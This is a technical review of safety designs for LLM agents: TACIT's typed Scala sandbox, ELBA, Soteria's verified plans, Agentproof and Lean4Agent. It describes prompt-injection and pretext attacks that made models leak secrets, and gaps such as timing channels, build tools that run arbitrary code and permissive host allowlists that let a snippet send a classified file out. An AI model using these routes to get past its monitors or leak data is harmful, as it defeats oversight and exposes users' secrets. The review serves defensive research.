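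According to Odersky and colleagues, the Scala compiler enforces safe mode on every snippet, but the software has not always worked this way. Earlier documentation from lampepfl described a plan to move to the compiler's safe mode from a separate validator that searched snippets for forbidden patterns. Later documentation still includes this weaker check but lists the compiler's safe mode as on by default.

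### The safety experiment

To test how well secrets were protected, Odersky and colleagues set up a sample software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They wrote 12 ordinary tasks, such as listing the project's web interfaces or summarizing a classified incident report. They paired each task with each of ten injections, for 120 trials. Some injections were plain instructions in code comments. Others were imitation system messages, claims that the secrets were only test data, or Scala code for reading the secrets.

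In another 11 trials, the user was the attacker. The user asked for secrets outright in five of them and used a pretext in the other six, such as an administrator urgently needing to replace passwords. Each model ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as ordinary strings. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model and type of request | Secure with wrapped secrets | Secure with ordinary strings |
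|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, injected text (120) | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, openly malicious (11) | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, all (131) | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, injected text (120) | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, openly malicious (11) | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5, all (131) | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the wrapper, Sonnet leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax in eleven. Ten of these thirteen leaks came from the few requests in which the user asked for the secrets. Injected text succeeded in three of 240 trials. On this evidence, the types add little protection against simple injections but a great deal against a hostile user.

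The unprotected figures probably understate the exposure. TACIT is meant to keep secrets from the company that hosts the model, and a model that summarizes an unwrapped incident report has already received any secrets in it, even if its answer reveals none. The protected figures, like ACE's perfect score on InjecAgent, follow from the design and show that the software behaved as intended in these trials. None of the attacks the paper describes targeted flaws in the compiler or library, where a determined attacker would look.

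The wrapper did not make the agents less useful. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the 120 ordinary trials with wrapped secrets and 83.3% with unwrapped ones, while MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3% respectively. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's gap is an artefact, because in the unprotected runs Sonnet often exceeded its limit on turns or time, or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

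### Results on AgentDojo

The team also adapted the four standard AgentDojo domains to TACIT and compared the results with the figures that CaMeL's developers had published for the same models. The percentages are the tasks completed:

| Domain | CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL, o4-mini | TACIT, o4-mini |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Workspace | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
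| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

With o4-mini, TACIT's completion rate was 29 percentage points lower than CaMeL's on workspace tasks and 21 points lower on Slack tasks. Odersky and colleagues call the two systems' usefulness comparable, which is fair for banking tasks but not for these.

In 963 attack trials per model, one attack succeeded against TACIT and one against CaMeL. In the TACIT trial, the user asked the agent to book a hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but also quoted the reviews, including the recommendation. AgentDojo counted this as a successful attack because the other hotel's name appeared in the output. Odersky and colleagues object that the policy allowed public reviews to reach the user, so the type system had nothing to block. They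 are right about the type system, but the user still read an advertisement written by an attacker, and TACIT does not protect against that.

These results are weaker evidence for type checking than they look. In the adapted domains, the tools that read emails, Slack messages, web pages and hotel reviews all return wrapped values, so most of the injected text never reached the main model. This amounts to isolating the planner. The purity rule also seems to have been looser here than in the main design. The printed signature of `sendMoney` requires no capability, and according to the model's instructions, side effects inside `map` happen immediately. If the compiler did allow payments inside `map`, a snippet could send money to an account number taken from a hostile file.

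### What typed code costs

Capture checking is new, so models have seen little code that uses it. To test whether this hurts agents' performance, the team compared TACIT with ordinary tool calls on two benchmarks. One of them, τ²-bench, simulates customer service for an airline and a shop. All three models tested, gpt-oss-120b, MiniMax M2.5 and DeepSeek V3.2, scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher in both domains when they wrote Scala. The researchers attribute the gains to the tools' structured results and the compiler's error messages.

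SWE-bench Lite has 300 real software problems from GitHub. MiniMax solved 41.7% of them with TACIT and 43.3% with ordinary tools, a difference of five problems. Programming agents normally rely on shell commands, which are less natural to express through TACIT's library.

On τ²-bench, the models had to retry between 0.32% and 7.93% of their snippets, depending on the model and domain. One or two further attempts were usually enough. Recurring errors included values that might be missing and unescaped dollar signs in text, neither of which involves capabilities. Once it is running, the compiler takes less than a second for a typical snippet. *What's in the Box* (2025), a paper on the underlying type system, reports that capture checking accounted for under 15% of the time spent compiling Scala's standard library.

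But the τ²-bench tools return ordinary, unwrapped values, so the benchmark measures how well models write typed Scala and leaves out the effect of hiding data from them. VirtusLab warns that this effect can be large, because agents are useful partly for reading files and emails, which they can't do if an administrator classifies too much.

Someone also has to write the library. TACIT's reusable part is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the descriptions of the τ²-bench tools take a few hundred lines per domain. Odersky and colleagues note that these descriptions are about as long as the JSON ones they replace.

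### Harmful code that passes the type check

A snippet can satisfy the type checker and still give a wrong answer, for instance by summing the wrong column of a spreadsheet. Odersky and colleagues exclude such errors from their goals. They also claim, too strongly, that any injection that does real harm must either leak private data or use a capability the agent was not given. An agent with write access to a project can delete the project's files, and an injected instruction to do so produces a well-typed snippet.

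TACIT also protects secrets from being read but not from being changed. The library lets a snippet wrap any text and write it to a classified file. According to Glama's copy of the documentation, an agent could overwrite the file that lists who may log in to the computer. A server setting can block writes to classified files, but it is off by default.

Timing can reveal secrets too. A function inside `map` might finish at once if a password begins with "a" and run for ten seconds otherwise. The cloud model receives only `Classified(****)`, but it can measure how long the answer took. The paper's guarantee doesn't cover such channels. Each use leaks little, but an agent that can repeat the test could recover a short password.

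External programs are a larger gap, because the type checker has no control over a command once it has started. The paper recommends a list of specific safe commands and gives `git diff` and `sbt`, Scala's build tool, as examples. But `sbt` runs build files that are Scala programs, so an agent allowed to edit a build file and start `sbt` can run any code outside safe mode. The sample configuration in the later documentation permits `sbt`, `java` and `make`, all of which can run code that the agent has just written. The paper advises combining TACIT with a sandbox where security is critical, and a sandbox is close to a requirement for a programming agent.

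New library functions can open further gaps. The later documentation describes functions that send a classified value to a web server without unwrapping it, for example so that the agent can log in to a service with a key it cannot read. The server must be on a list of permitted hosts. The snippet supplies one list, and the administrator can add another that the snippet cannot override. According to the documentation, if the administrator sets none, only the snippet's list applies. A hostile model could then list the attacker's server and send it a classified file, in code that the compiler accepts.

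The checker may also contain errors. Odersky and colleagues cite machine-checked proofs for the core of capture checking, and *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) extends such proofs to a system that can reason about whole kinds of capability. These proofs cover small mathematical models of the language, not the compiler's code. Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode's capability safety and purity have yet to be proved. Lightrun's *Unsound application of boxed functions*, a copy of an early bug report, shows a short program that the capture checker wrongly accepted. The bug is old, but Scala's documentation still describes capture checking as "highly experimental and unstable".

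Developers are building on it anyway. *LACUNA* (2026) uses it for another agent design, and Scala Days' *Making the AI agents safe with Scala* announces a joint EPFL and VirtusLab project to turn TACIT into an agent for everyday use.

### A similar design in Haskell

Odersky and colleagues chose Scala because they consider it the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in its types. They note that Haskell can separate pure code from code with effects but has no built-in capabilities. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, show that Haskell's existing features can still do much to limit generated code. Their system, ELBA, makes the agent an ordinary function that takes a prompt and generates a program of whatever type the surrounding code expects.

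Haskell records a program's effects in its result type. If a web calculator expects an `Int`, a whole number, the generated program cannot perform any effects. A visitor might ask the calculator to delete every file on the server before computing a factorial. A program that deleted the files would have a type that allows input and output rather than `Int`, so the compiler would reject it.

For tasks that need some effects, the developer defines a narrower type. Zhou and colleagues describe an agent that compiles bibliographies and may write only entries from DBLP, a database of computer-science publications. Its program must have the type `BibIO`, which permits searching DBLP, fetching an entry and adding an entry to a file. The add operation accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, which the program can obtain only by fetching from DBLP. The program can therefore sort and filter the fetched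 entries in any way, but it cannot add an invented entry to the file.

This rule protects the integrity of the file because `Trusted` restricts where a value may come from. TACIT's wrapper restricts where a value may go, which does not protect the file's integrity. A payment tool could likewise accept only account numbers from the user's saved contacts, so the compiler would reject a plan that pays an account number copied from an invoice.

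A generated program can also call the agent function again, for example after reading a search result. The program this call generates has to fit the type expected at that point, so a sub-agent inherits its parent's limits and may get stricter ones. ELBA agents can therefore respond to what they read while staying within the policy.

Zhou and colleagues' ELBA requires developers to write the whole application in Haskell, so that the code around the agent passes the same type checker as the code the agent generates. TACIT doesn't check the surrounding code. Existing agents can therefore use TACIT, but it protects the files only if those agents have no other way to reach them.

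## Proving that a plan respects tool contracts and policies

Labels and types can settle whether a plan may send bank details or write to a file, but many rules depend on more specific facts. For example, an airline may let its agent cancel a reservation only if the passenger has not flown any part of it. A plan that obeys this rule and one that breaks it can call the same cancellation tool with the same kind of data. To tell them apart, a checker has to work out what must be true before each call and whether the earlier steps guarantee it.

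### Preconditions, postconditions and provers

A tool contract has two parts. The precondition must be true before the agent calls the tool, and the postcondition is true afterwards. Suppose that a tool called `pay` requires an amount no larger than the current balance, and that the balance afterwards is lower by that amount. A user wants the agent to pay the rent and the electricity bill if there is enough money:

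```
balance = get_balance()
if balance >= 900:
    pay(to="landlord", amount=700)
    pay(to="electricity", amount=200)
```

Before the first payment, the checker can rely on a balance of at least 900, which covers the rent. It then uses the postcondition to derive that at least 200 remains, which covers the electricity. If the planner had written 800 instead of 900, the checker would reject the plan, because only 100 might remain. Tony Hoare, a British computer scientist, set out this way of reasoning about programs in 1969.

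Automated provers can do the reasoning. One of them, Z3, searches for values that make a formula true. To prove that one statement follows from another, a checker asks Z3 for a case in which the first is true and the second is false:

```
claim:       balance >= 900  ⇒  balance - 700 >= 200
ask Z3 for:  balance >= 900  and  balance - 700 < 200
```

If Z3 shows that no such balance exists, the claim is proved. With 800 in place of 900, Z3 would find a counterexample, such as a balance of 850. Dafny is a programming language with a built-in verifier. Programmers write contracts next to their code, and Dafny turns them into formulas for Z3. Meijer suggested both tools for checking agents' workflows.

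### What must stay unchanged

In Meijer's file example, the user asks the agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the model writes a workflow with a single call, `delete_file("*.txt")`, which deletes every text file. Whether a checker rejects this workflow depends on how complete the contracts are. Meijer starts with one postcondition for the tool and one for the plan:

```
delete_file(pattern):  every file that matches pattern is gone
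the plan:              foo.txt and bar.txt are gone
```

Both names match `*.txt`, so the plan passes. Meijer doesn't blame the model for this, since nothing in the contracts requires any other file to survive. They lack a frame condition, which is a statement of what stays unchanged. The name comes from the frame problem, which John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described in 1969. With frame conditions, the contracts become:

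```
delete_file(pattern):  every file that matches pattern is gone
                       every other file is as it was
the plan:              foo.txt and bar.txt are gone
                       every other file is as it was
```

A prover can now refute the plan with a counterexample in which the folder also contains `notes.txt`. The plan's own frame condition causes this rejection. The tool's frame condition is needed for a correct plan to pass, because a plan that deletes the two files one at a time can be proved correct only if that condition guarantees that `delete_file("foo.txt")` leaves `notes.txt` unchanged.

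Meijer prints a frame condition only for the tool and reports that the `*.txt` workflow then fails to verify. The workflow would still pass under the contracts as he prints them, because deleting every text file also deletes the two that the user named.

Even the full contracts cover only files. They don't rule out that `delete_file` also empties the mailbox, and nobody could list everything a tool leaves unchanged. In Dafny, a contract instead lists which of the program's own data an operation may change, and the verifier treats the rest of that data as unchanged. Such a contract is still only a claim about the tool, and if the claim is false, a proof that relies on it doesn't guarantee what the plan will do.

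### Plans as states and guarded transitions

He, Desai and colleagues (2026), in *SOTERIA*, apply contracts to whole plans. Their system, built at Princeton University and the data company Snowflake, also checks policies about sequences of calls, such as a rule that one call must come before another. Their running example is a customer-service agent for an airline, taken from τ²-bench. A user asks it to cancel a reservation, and the planner writes a plan that amounts to this:

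```
LOOKUP:       resv = Get-Resv(rid)              → CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE:    hrs = Hours-Diff(resv.ts, time)   → CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES:  if hrs <= 24                      → DO_CANCEL
              otherwise                         → NOT_PERMITTED
DO_CANCEL:    res = Cancel-Resv(rid, reason)    → DONE
```

Each name on the left is a state, and each arrow is a transition to another state. A transition can make at most one tool call, and a guard such as `hrs <= 24` determines whether the plan may take that transition. The plan ends in `DONE` if it has completed the task, or in `NOT_PERMITTED` if it cannot safely continue.

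A transition can also ask a language model to make a judgement, such as choosing flights with enough seats. The planner then states a condition that the answer must meet. The checker assumes the condition holds, and Soteria tests it during the run.

To check a plan, Soteria works out what is known in each state. It writes this knowledge as a formula, Σ(s) for state `s`, and carries it along the transitions:

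```
known after one transition:  Σ(s) ∧ guard ∧ (what the action establishes)

if several transitions t1, ..., tm lead to state s':
    Σ(s') = (known after t1) ∨ ... ∨ (known after tm)
```

The symbol ∧ means "and", and ∨ means "or". After `LOOKUP`, the postcondition of `Get-Resv` holds. After `CHECK_AGE`, the postcondition of `Hours-Diff` also holds, and in `DO_CANCEL`, `hrs` is at most 24. If a plan could also reach `DO_CANCEL` because the customer had bought insurance, the checker would establish there that the booking was recent or insured, a distinction that joining two labels would lose.

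The checker must finish every state that leads to `s'` before it computes Σ(s'), so Soteria rejects any plan whose transitions form a cycle. A plan can repeat an action only by applying it to each item of a list.

### The three checks

Soteria translates its checks into Dafny. With P for the precondition of a tool and g for a guard, they are:

```
contracts:  Σ(s) ∧ g  ⇒  P(arguments)      for every tool call

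progress:   Σ(s) is satisfiable            for every non-final state
            Σ(s)  ⇒  g1 ∨ g2 ∨ ... ∨ gn    for every state with guards

policy:     the log of calls satisfies φ   for every rule φ and

every path to a final state
```

The contract check uses the same reasoning as the payment example. The progress check looks for two kinds of planning mistakes. The first is a state that no run can reach, which is the case if Σ(s) is unsatisfiable, meaning that no values make it true. The second is a state where the plan can get stuck because all the guards can be false at once. For example, a plan with one branch for `hrs < 24` and another for `hrs > 24` gets stuck on a booking made exactly 24 hours ago.

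For the policy check, Soteria adds a log to the translated plan. The log exists only in the proof. It records the order of the calls with their arguments and results, and it lists for each variable the tools whose outputs contributed to its current value. A policy is a statement about this log. The rule about flown reservations is:

```
φ1:  for every call c to Cancel-Resv
     there is a call d to No-Flown such that
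         d comes before c,
         d and c have the same reservation number, and
         d returned true
```

A rule can also require a later call. One rule for file tasks requires the agent to read back every file it has written. A run-time monitor can block a write, but it cannot make the agent read the file afterward. The static check establishes that every path through the plan includes the reading step.

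Rules about where a value comes from can still accept wrong values. He and colleagues give the example of a refund, whose amount must derive from a lookup of the same reservation. The log records that the amount came from `Get-Resv`, but not from which call, so the check would accept a plan that looked up two reservations and refunded one customer the price of the other's ticket. He and colleagues did this deliberately and leave further requirements to separate conditions. The rule also permits arithmetic, so an amount ten times the ticket price would still count as derived from the lookup.

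By these definitions, a plan that goes straight to a halting state passes every check, because it never calls a tool. Only testing can show whether the planner writes plans that complete the task.

### A cancellation without the flown-status check

The cancellation plan above passes the progress check at `CHECK_RULES`, since `hrs` is either at most 24 or more than 24. It also obeys the airline's rule that a booking must be less than a day old. But at `DONE`, the log contains one call to `Cancel-Resv`, so φ1 requires a matching call to `No-Flown`, which the plan never makes. Dafny reports that the assertion for φ1 fails, and Soteria rejects the plan before any lookup runs.

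Soteria then tells the planner which rule failed and adds advice for that type of mistake. The planner repairs the plan by inserting a state:

```
LOOKUP:       resv = Get-Resv(rid)              → CHECK_FLOWN
CHECK_FLOWN:  ok = No-Flown(rid)                → CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE:    hrs = Hours-Diff(resv.ts, time)   → CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES:  if ok and hrs <= 24               → DO_CANCEL
              otherwise                         → NOT_PERMITTED
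DO_CANCEL:    res = Cancel-Resv(rid, reason)    → DONE
```

The two versions compare as follows at `DONE`:

| What φ1 requires | First plan | Repaired plan |
|---|---|---|
| A call to `No-Flown` | Missing | Present |
| It comes before the cancellation | | Second call, before the fourth |
| Same reservation number | | Both calls use `rid` |
| The result is true | | The guard requires `ok` |

The plan needs the last condition because `No-Flown` can return false, so calling it is not enough. He and colleagues print a run of their repaired plan in which `No-Flown` returns true, and the only guard shown checks the booking's age. A plan with only that guard would fail their own rule, so the version here also tests `ok`.

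The checker proves that the plan cancels only if `No-Flown` has returned true, which it can do without data on whether this customer has flown. The proof assumes that `No-Flown` returns the correct answer, as its contract requires.

### Reusable sub-plans

Many requests combine standard procedures, such as a cancellation and a refund, that each have their own rules. Soteria keeps a library of sub-plans that a developer prepares with a model's help and verifies in advance. Each has a contract and ends by either completing the request or safely refusing it. The planner can call a sub-plan like a tool, with one branch for each outcome. When Soteria verifies the larger plan, it uses only the sub-plan's contract, without re-examining its internal states.

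He and colleagues measured the effect with GPT-5.4-mini on the airline tasks, allowing eight retries for each plan:

| | With sub-plans | Without |
|---|---|---|
| Median number of states in a plan | 8 | 11 |
| Plans verified at the first attempt | 48.5% | 23.3% |
| Plans verified within the retry limit | 65 of 68 | 38 of 60 |

Without sub-plans, the planner kept breaking policies across attempts, because fixing a violation meant redesigning the plan. With sub-plans, most of the remaining errors were in syntax, which the planner could fix from the error message.

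This is a large improvement, but part of it comes from moving work to the developer. The developer has already written a correct cancellation procedure, so the planner only has to call it. Prewritten procedures don't help with requests they don't cover.

### When the prover finds no proof

A prover may fail to settle a condition that is true. Z3 reliably decides many formulas about whole numbers and equality, but Soteria's policies combine "for every call" with "there is a call", and no algorithm can decide all formulas of that kind. Z3 may then return "unknown" or keep searching. Soteria gives it ten seconds per state, then treats the condition as unproved.

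If a plan fails for any reason, the planner gets the error report and tries again, up to eight times in the main experiments. If no attempt passes completely, Soteria goes ahead with the plan that satisfied the most checks and lists the unproved rules as warnings in the prompt of the language model that executes the plan. A run-time monitor blocks any call that would break a rule, whether or not the plan passed.

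Soteria thus normally uses verification to improve plans and relies on the monitor for the guarantee. It also has a strict mode, which runs only fully verified plans and permits only the calls in them. In this mode, a timeout can leave the user's request undone.

### Results on 207 tasks

He et al. tested Soteria on 50 airline tasks and 114 retail tasks from τ²-bench, and on 43 tasks from Toolathlon, a benchmark of long office and file-handling jobs. They compared it with four baselines that used the same models. The first had only the written policy in its prompt as a safeguard. The second, NeMo Guardrails, uses a language model to judge every call. The other two, AgentSpec and Agent Behavioral Contracts, enforce formal rules during the run, without a verified plan.

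A task counts as a success if the agent completes it without breaking a rule. The table shows Soteria's success rate, with the best baseline for the same model in brackets:

| Model | Airline | Retail | Toolathlon |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 60.0% (50.0%) | 35.1% (20.2%) | 11.6% (2.3%) |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 62.0% (36.0%) | 45.6% (38.6%) | 16.3% (2.3%) |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.0% (30.0%) | 56.1% (31.6%) | 9.3% (4.7%) |
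| Claude Opus 4.6 | 88.0% (56.0%) | 90.4% (46.5%) | 18.6% (11.6%) |

Soteria broke no rules with any model. The baselines' rate of rule-abiding runs never exceeded 93%.

That perfect record follows from the design. The researchers scored conformance on the same 98 formal rules that Soteria's monitor enforces, and they corrected and added rules while auditing the results. A breach of the airline's written policy that the formal rules miss would count as conformance. He and colleagues describe an unguarded run in which the agent upgraded a reservation to business class so that it would qualify for cancellation. They call this a workaround that the policy does not permit, but their formal rule allows a cancellation if an earlier lookup shows a business-class cabin. An agent that upgraded the reservation, looked it up again, ran the flown-status check and then cancelled would satisfy the cancellation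 rules as printed.

The success rates are more informative because they also depend on the outcome. An agent that always refused would succeed at some tasks where the policy forbids what the customer wants, but it would fail wherever the customer is entitled to a change. Without safeguards, Opus completed 53.5% of retail tasks, even counting runs that broke the rules. With Soteria, it completed 90.4%, so most of the gain has little to do with preventing violations. The unguarded agent often collected the information it needed and then transferred the customer to a human. It made the required change in only 57% of the tasks that called for one, whereas Opus made it every time when given a plan that named the change and its arguments. The baselines had the written policy but not the library of sub-plans, so the comparison also measures the value of writing out the procedures in advance.

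On Toolathlon, whether Opus does better with or without Soteria depends on how much the rules matter to the user. Opus completed 30.2% of the tasks without safeguards and 18.6% with Soteria. Excluding runs that broke a rule lowers the score without safeguards to 11.6%. Some of these rules prevent real damage, such as a ban on dropping database tables, while others require good habits, such as listing a folder before writing to it. A user who only wants the file written would have been better off without Soteria.

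Most of the main results come from a single attempt per task. When the researchers ran GPT-5.4-mini five times on the airline tasks, with three planning retries instead of eight, Soteria averaged 50.8% and AgentSpec 48.0%, with overlapping confidence intervals. A verified plan may therefore add little to what run-time rules achieve when the planner has the fewest retries. The differences were much larger with Opus, but nobody has repeated those runs.

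Soteria also changes what a task costs:

| Average cost per task | Airline | Retail | Toolathlon |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 with Soteria | $0.796 | $0.640 | $0.431 |
| Claude Opus 4.6, no safeguard | $0.318 | $0.370 | $0.972 |
| GPT-5.4-mini with Soteria | $0.125 | $0.154 | $0.033 |
| GPT-5.4-mini, no safeguard | $0.031 | $0.036 | $0.045 |

In the customer-service tasks, Soteria writes a new plan after each customer message, which doubles the cost with Opus and quadruples it with GPT-5.4-mini. A Toolathlon task needs only one plan, and the agent then wastes fewer steps.

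None of these tasks contained injected instructions, so the experiments measure protection against a planner's mistakes and not against attacks.

### Checking workflow graphs against automata

A simpler method ignores the data and checks only the order of the steps. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) applies it to workflows that developers write in common agent frameworks such as LangGraph, CrewAI, AutoGen and Google ADK. The software extracts a graph from the code, in which each node is a step, such as a tool call, a model call or a human review. It then runs six structural checks, including that every step leads somewhere and that every exit is reachable. In one example, a developer adds a step that drafts replies to ordinary emails but forgets to connect it to the sending step, and the checker prints the path to the dead end.

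For policies about order, Agentproof uses automata. An automaton is a small machine that changes its state as events occur. The policy that each email draft needs a human review becomes:

| State | After a draft | After a review |
|---|---|---|
| Idle | Waiting | Idle |
| Waiting | Violation | Idle |

Agentproof starts at the workflow's entry with the automaton in its idle state and explores every combination of step and automaton state that the graph allows. If the workflow can loop from drafting to sending and back to drafting, the automaton is in its waiting state when the workflow reaches the second draft, and the checker reports the path. The number of combinations is at most the number of steps times the number of automaton states, so the search always finishes, with no risk of a prover timing out. The structural checks took about a tenth of a second on an artificial graph of 5,000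 nodes.

The printed automaton misses a workflow that drafts one email and ends without a review, because the automaton stops in the waiting state, which is not a violation. Xavier and colleagues use the same form for a rule that a deployment needs approval. By their definitions, a workflow that deploys once would pass even if it never asked for approval or asked only afterwards. They report that the software caught a missing review after a draft, so it may treat the end of a workflow differently than the printed version does. A separate check can require a human step on every path to a sensitive tool, which is closer to what most companies would mean by approval.

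Xavier and colleagues ran the software on 18 workflows they had written themselves, some with deliberate faults. It found structural faults in five. Ten had no human review step, though some of those arguably didn't need one. The team also wrote 15 policies for the automata and tried them on ten random runs of each workflow. The static check found everything those runs revealed, plus the missing review, which was on a path none of the runs had taken. The test shows that the software can find such faults but, as the researchers acknowledge, it doesn't show how common they are in practice.

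Because Agentproof treats every branch as possible, it can raise false alarms about paths that no run would take, and Xavier and colleagues have not measured how often this happens. The extraction can also go wrong. For LangGraph, the software identifies a human review step by the word "human" in its name, so it would probably mistake a step called `humanize_reply` for human review.

For the airline, an automaton could require a call to `No-Flown` in the right place, but not that the call was about the same reservation or that it returned true. Soteria needs a prover because it tracks these values.

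### Lean4Agent

*Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) checks whether the steps of a workflow fit together. It uses Lean, a programming language and proof assistant for writing proofs that a computer can check. A language model reads the instructions for each step and writes a precondition and a postcondition. Lean then checks that earlier steps establish each later step's precondition.

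Most of these steps are instructions to a language model, such as "find the cause of the bug", for which nobody can write a reliable contract. Wang and colleagues therefore make an assumption, which they call LLMExec:

```
if the precondition of a step holds,
then the model can produce a result that satisfies the postcondition
```

A workflow that passes the check is consistent as written, but its runs may still fail because the check assumes that the model can succeed, not that it always will. Separate software examines completed runs to find the step that went wrong, partly by using a language model as a judge.

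The check finds mistakes that are easy to overlook. In one workflow for fixing software, each step's instructions referred to what previous steps had found, but the step started without the earlier conversation. In another, for answering multiple-choice questions, the model evaluated the options in turn in the same conversation, so its evaluation of one option could influence the next.

To test whether passing matters, Wang and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.6 write 40 workflows, and chose three that passed and three that failed for each benchmark. Five other models then ran them on 50 hard software problems from SWE-bench Verified and on 100 questions about AI papers from ELAIP-Bench:

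| Average score over five models | Passing workflows | Failing workflows |
|---|---|---|
| Software problems | 58.27% | 43.47% |
| Questions about papers | 36.60% | 27.53% |

Passing workflows did better with every model. Smaller models did not always gain more, but the largest difference, 27 percentage points on the software problems, was for Gemma-4-31B, one of the two small models. With only three workflows in each group, one unusually good or bad workflow could account for much of the difference. The passing workflows also tended to have better retry loops and more precise variables, so the check may partly select workflows that were better written in general.

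Wang and colleagues also used the reports on failed runs to revise workflows that had passed. Running the revised versions on the same problems raised the share of solved software problems by a further 7.47 percentage points. Part of this gain came from another attempt guided by the failing tests. No such feedback was available for the questions about papers. On 20 of these that the original workflow had got wrong, their method solved about seven percentage points more than a plain rewrite by a model.

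Lean4Agent improves reliability, but none of these results concern safety. A workflow that steals a user's email can still have consistent steps. LLMExec is also the wrong assumption for security, because a model that has read a hostile email may do something other than what its step requires.

### Plans that come with proofs

In Soteria, the checker has to find the proof and may run out of time. In the approach Meijer presented in a June 2026 talk, which adapts Necula's proof-carrying code, the planner finds the proof, so the checker only has to check that each step is valid.

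The plan has to be in a form that a proof can take apart. Lean has a type for programs with side effects, `IO`, but Meijer points out that such a program is a black box, which Lean can run but not inspect. He would have the model return a data structure that describes the program instead. AI Engineer illustrates this in its write-up of the talk with a small language for handling files. Shortened and with other names, the definitions are:

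```
inductive Plan where
  | finish : String → Plan
  | read   : String → (String → Plan) → Plan
  | delete : String → Plan → Plan

inductive Harmless : Plan → Prop where
  | finish (answer : String) : Harmless (.finish answer)
  | read (path : String) (next : String → Plan)
      (h : ∀ text, Harmless (next text)) :
      Harmless (.read path next)
```

The first definition lets a plan finish with an answer, read a file and continue with its text, or delete a file and continue. The second definition is the policy. A plan is harmless if it finishes immediately, or if it reads a file and the rest of the plan is harmless for every text (∀) the file might contain. The policy has no rule for `delete`, so nobody can prove that a plan containing a deletion is harmless.

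For a plan that counts the characters in a file, the planner would deliver:

```
def countChars : Plan :=
  .read "notes.txt" (fun text => .finish (toString text.length))

theorem countChars_ok : Harmless countChars := by
  apply Harmless.read
  intro text
  exact Harmless.finish _
```

The proof has one step for each part of the plan. It applies the rule for reading, takes an arbitrary text, and applies the rule for finishing. The executor accepts only a plan paired with such a proof, so if a compromised planner adds a deletion, the plan will not run. The planner can try any number of proofs, because Lean rejects the wrong ones.

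Checking a finished proof is usually much easier than finding one, so this design moves the risk of running out of time from the checker to the planner. If the model can't find a proof for a safe plan, the user still gets nothing, just as when Soteria times out in strict mode. The proof in this example is easy because the policy only forbids one kind of step. A proof that the airline's plan satisfies φ1 would have to track reservation numbers and results, and Meijer doesn't report how often models can write such proofs or what they cost.

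The proof also covers only the plan's description. AI Engineer notes that an interpreter could secretly delete a file during a `read`, and that the policy would not stop a plan from reading a file it should not see. The interpreter is therefore part of the trusted base, along with Lean's proof checker and the definition of `Harmless`.

Meijer said his talk was not a product pitch, but he has a professional interest in the idea's success. He appeared as a research scholar at Leibniz Labs, which AI Engineer's *I've never seen anything scarier than an LLM with tool calls* (2026) associates with his work on verifying agents' actions. AI Engineer's *Erik Meijer* lists his current projects as Universalis and Automind, which are meant to let agents act without causing unchecked harm. If these become products, his interest is also commercial, so the lack of measurements matters more than it would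 in a proposal from someone with no stake in it.

Meijer has also promoted a version in which the planner writes no proof. Earlier in the year, *Return of the Theorem* (Meijer, 2026) proposed an architecture in which an automated solver checks each plan against a company's business rules, much as Soteria does. At the end of the June talk, he pointed to an implementation of plans with proofs by Nada Amin of Harvard and other academics, which uses a different language from his own.

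## Writing the rules that plans are checked against

A prover can show that a plan obeys a rule, but not that the rule is the one its author intended. If someone forgets a rule, words it badly or describes a tool wrongly, the proof still succeeds and the plan can still do harm.

### Three ways a valid proof can mislead

Suppose a shop wants a manager to approve any refund above $500, and a developer writes this rule for its agent:

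```
for every call refund(order, amount, card) with amount > 500:
    an earlier call ask_manager(order, amount) returned true
```

The shop also expects refunds to go back to the card used for the order, but nobody has written a rule for this. The checker therefore accepts a plan that gets the manager's approval for an $800 refund and sends the money to a different card.

Another plan refunds $400 twice for the same order without asking anybody. The shop cared about the total refunded, but the formula checks each call separately, so the existing rule misstates what the shop intended.

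Even a correct rule fails if a tool's contract describes the tool incorrectly. According to its contract, `ask_manager` returns `true` only if the manager has approved, but it also returns `true` when the manager hasn't answered within an hour, because a programmer didn't want customers to wait. A plan that waits for `true` satisfies the rule, and the shop pays out $800 without approval.

Each of these mistakes takes different knowledge to find. The shop's owner might notice that no rule mentions cards. Somebody who can read formulas might think of the split refund. Somebody would have to test the tool or read its code to find the timeout. Soteria partly tests contracts during the run by comparing each result with the tool's postcondition and stopping if they disagree. This would catch a cancellation tool that returns a reservation still marked as active, but not the timeout in `ask_manager`,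 because a `true` after an hour's silence looks the same as a real approval.

### Users, developers and models as rule-writers

ACE leaves most of this work to users, who label their data and requests. Each label is easy to choose, since a user doesn't need to know any logic to label a bank statement as financial. But users have to choose many labels, and a label can't express a requirement such as approval before a refund.

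Developers can write such requirements, as they did with the types that limit ELBA's programs and the automata that Agentproof runs on workflows. But the writer has to know the company's policy, the tools and the rule language, and few people know all three. Experts also make mistakes. Meijer's email rule, for example, named a tool that his workflow never called.

A language model can draft dozens of formulas from a company's existing policy document in minutes. This saves most of the writing, but someone still has to compare each formula with the policy. That can be harder than writing the formula, because it's easy to approve a plausible draft without checking it carefully.

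### How Soteria's rules were written

He and colleagues gave a model the written policy and the tools' definitions, and it drafted a contract for each tool and a set of rules about sequences of calls. They then inspected the drafts by hand and wrote formulas for cases the model had missed. They also went through the policy to check that each relevant clause had at least one formula.

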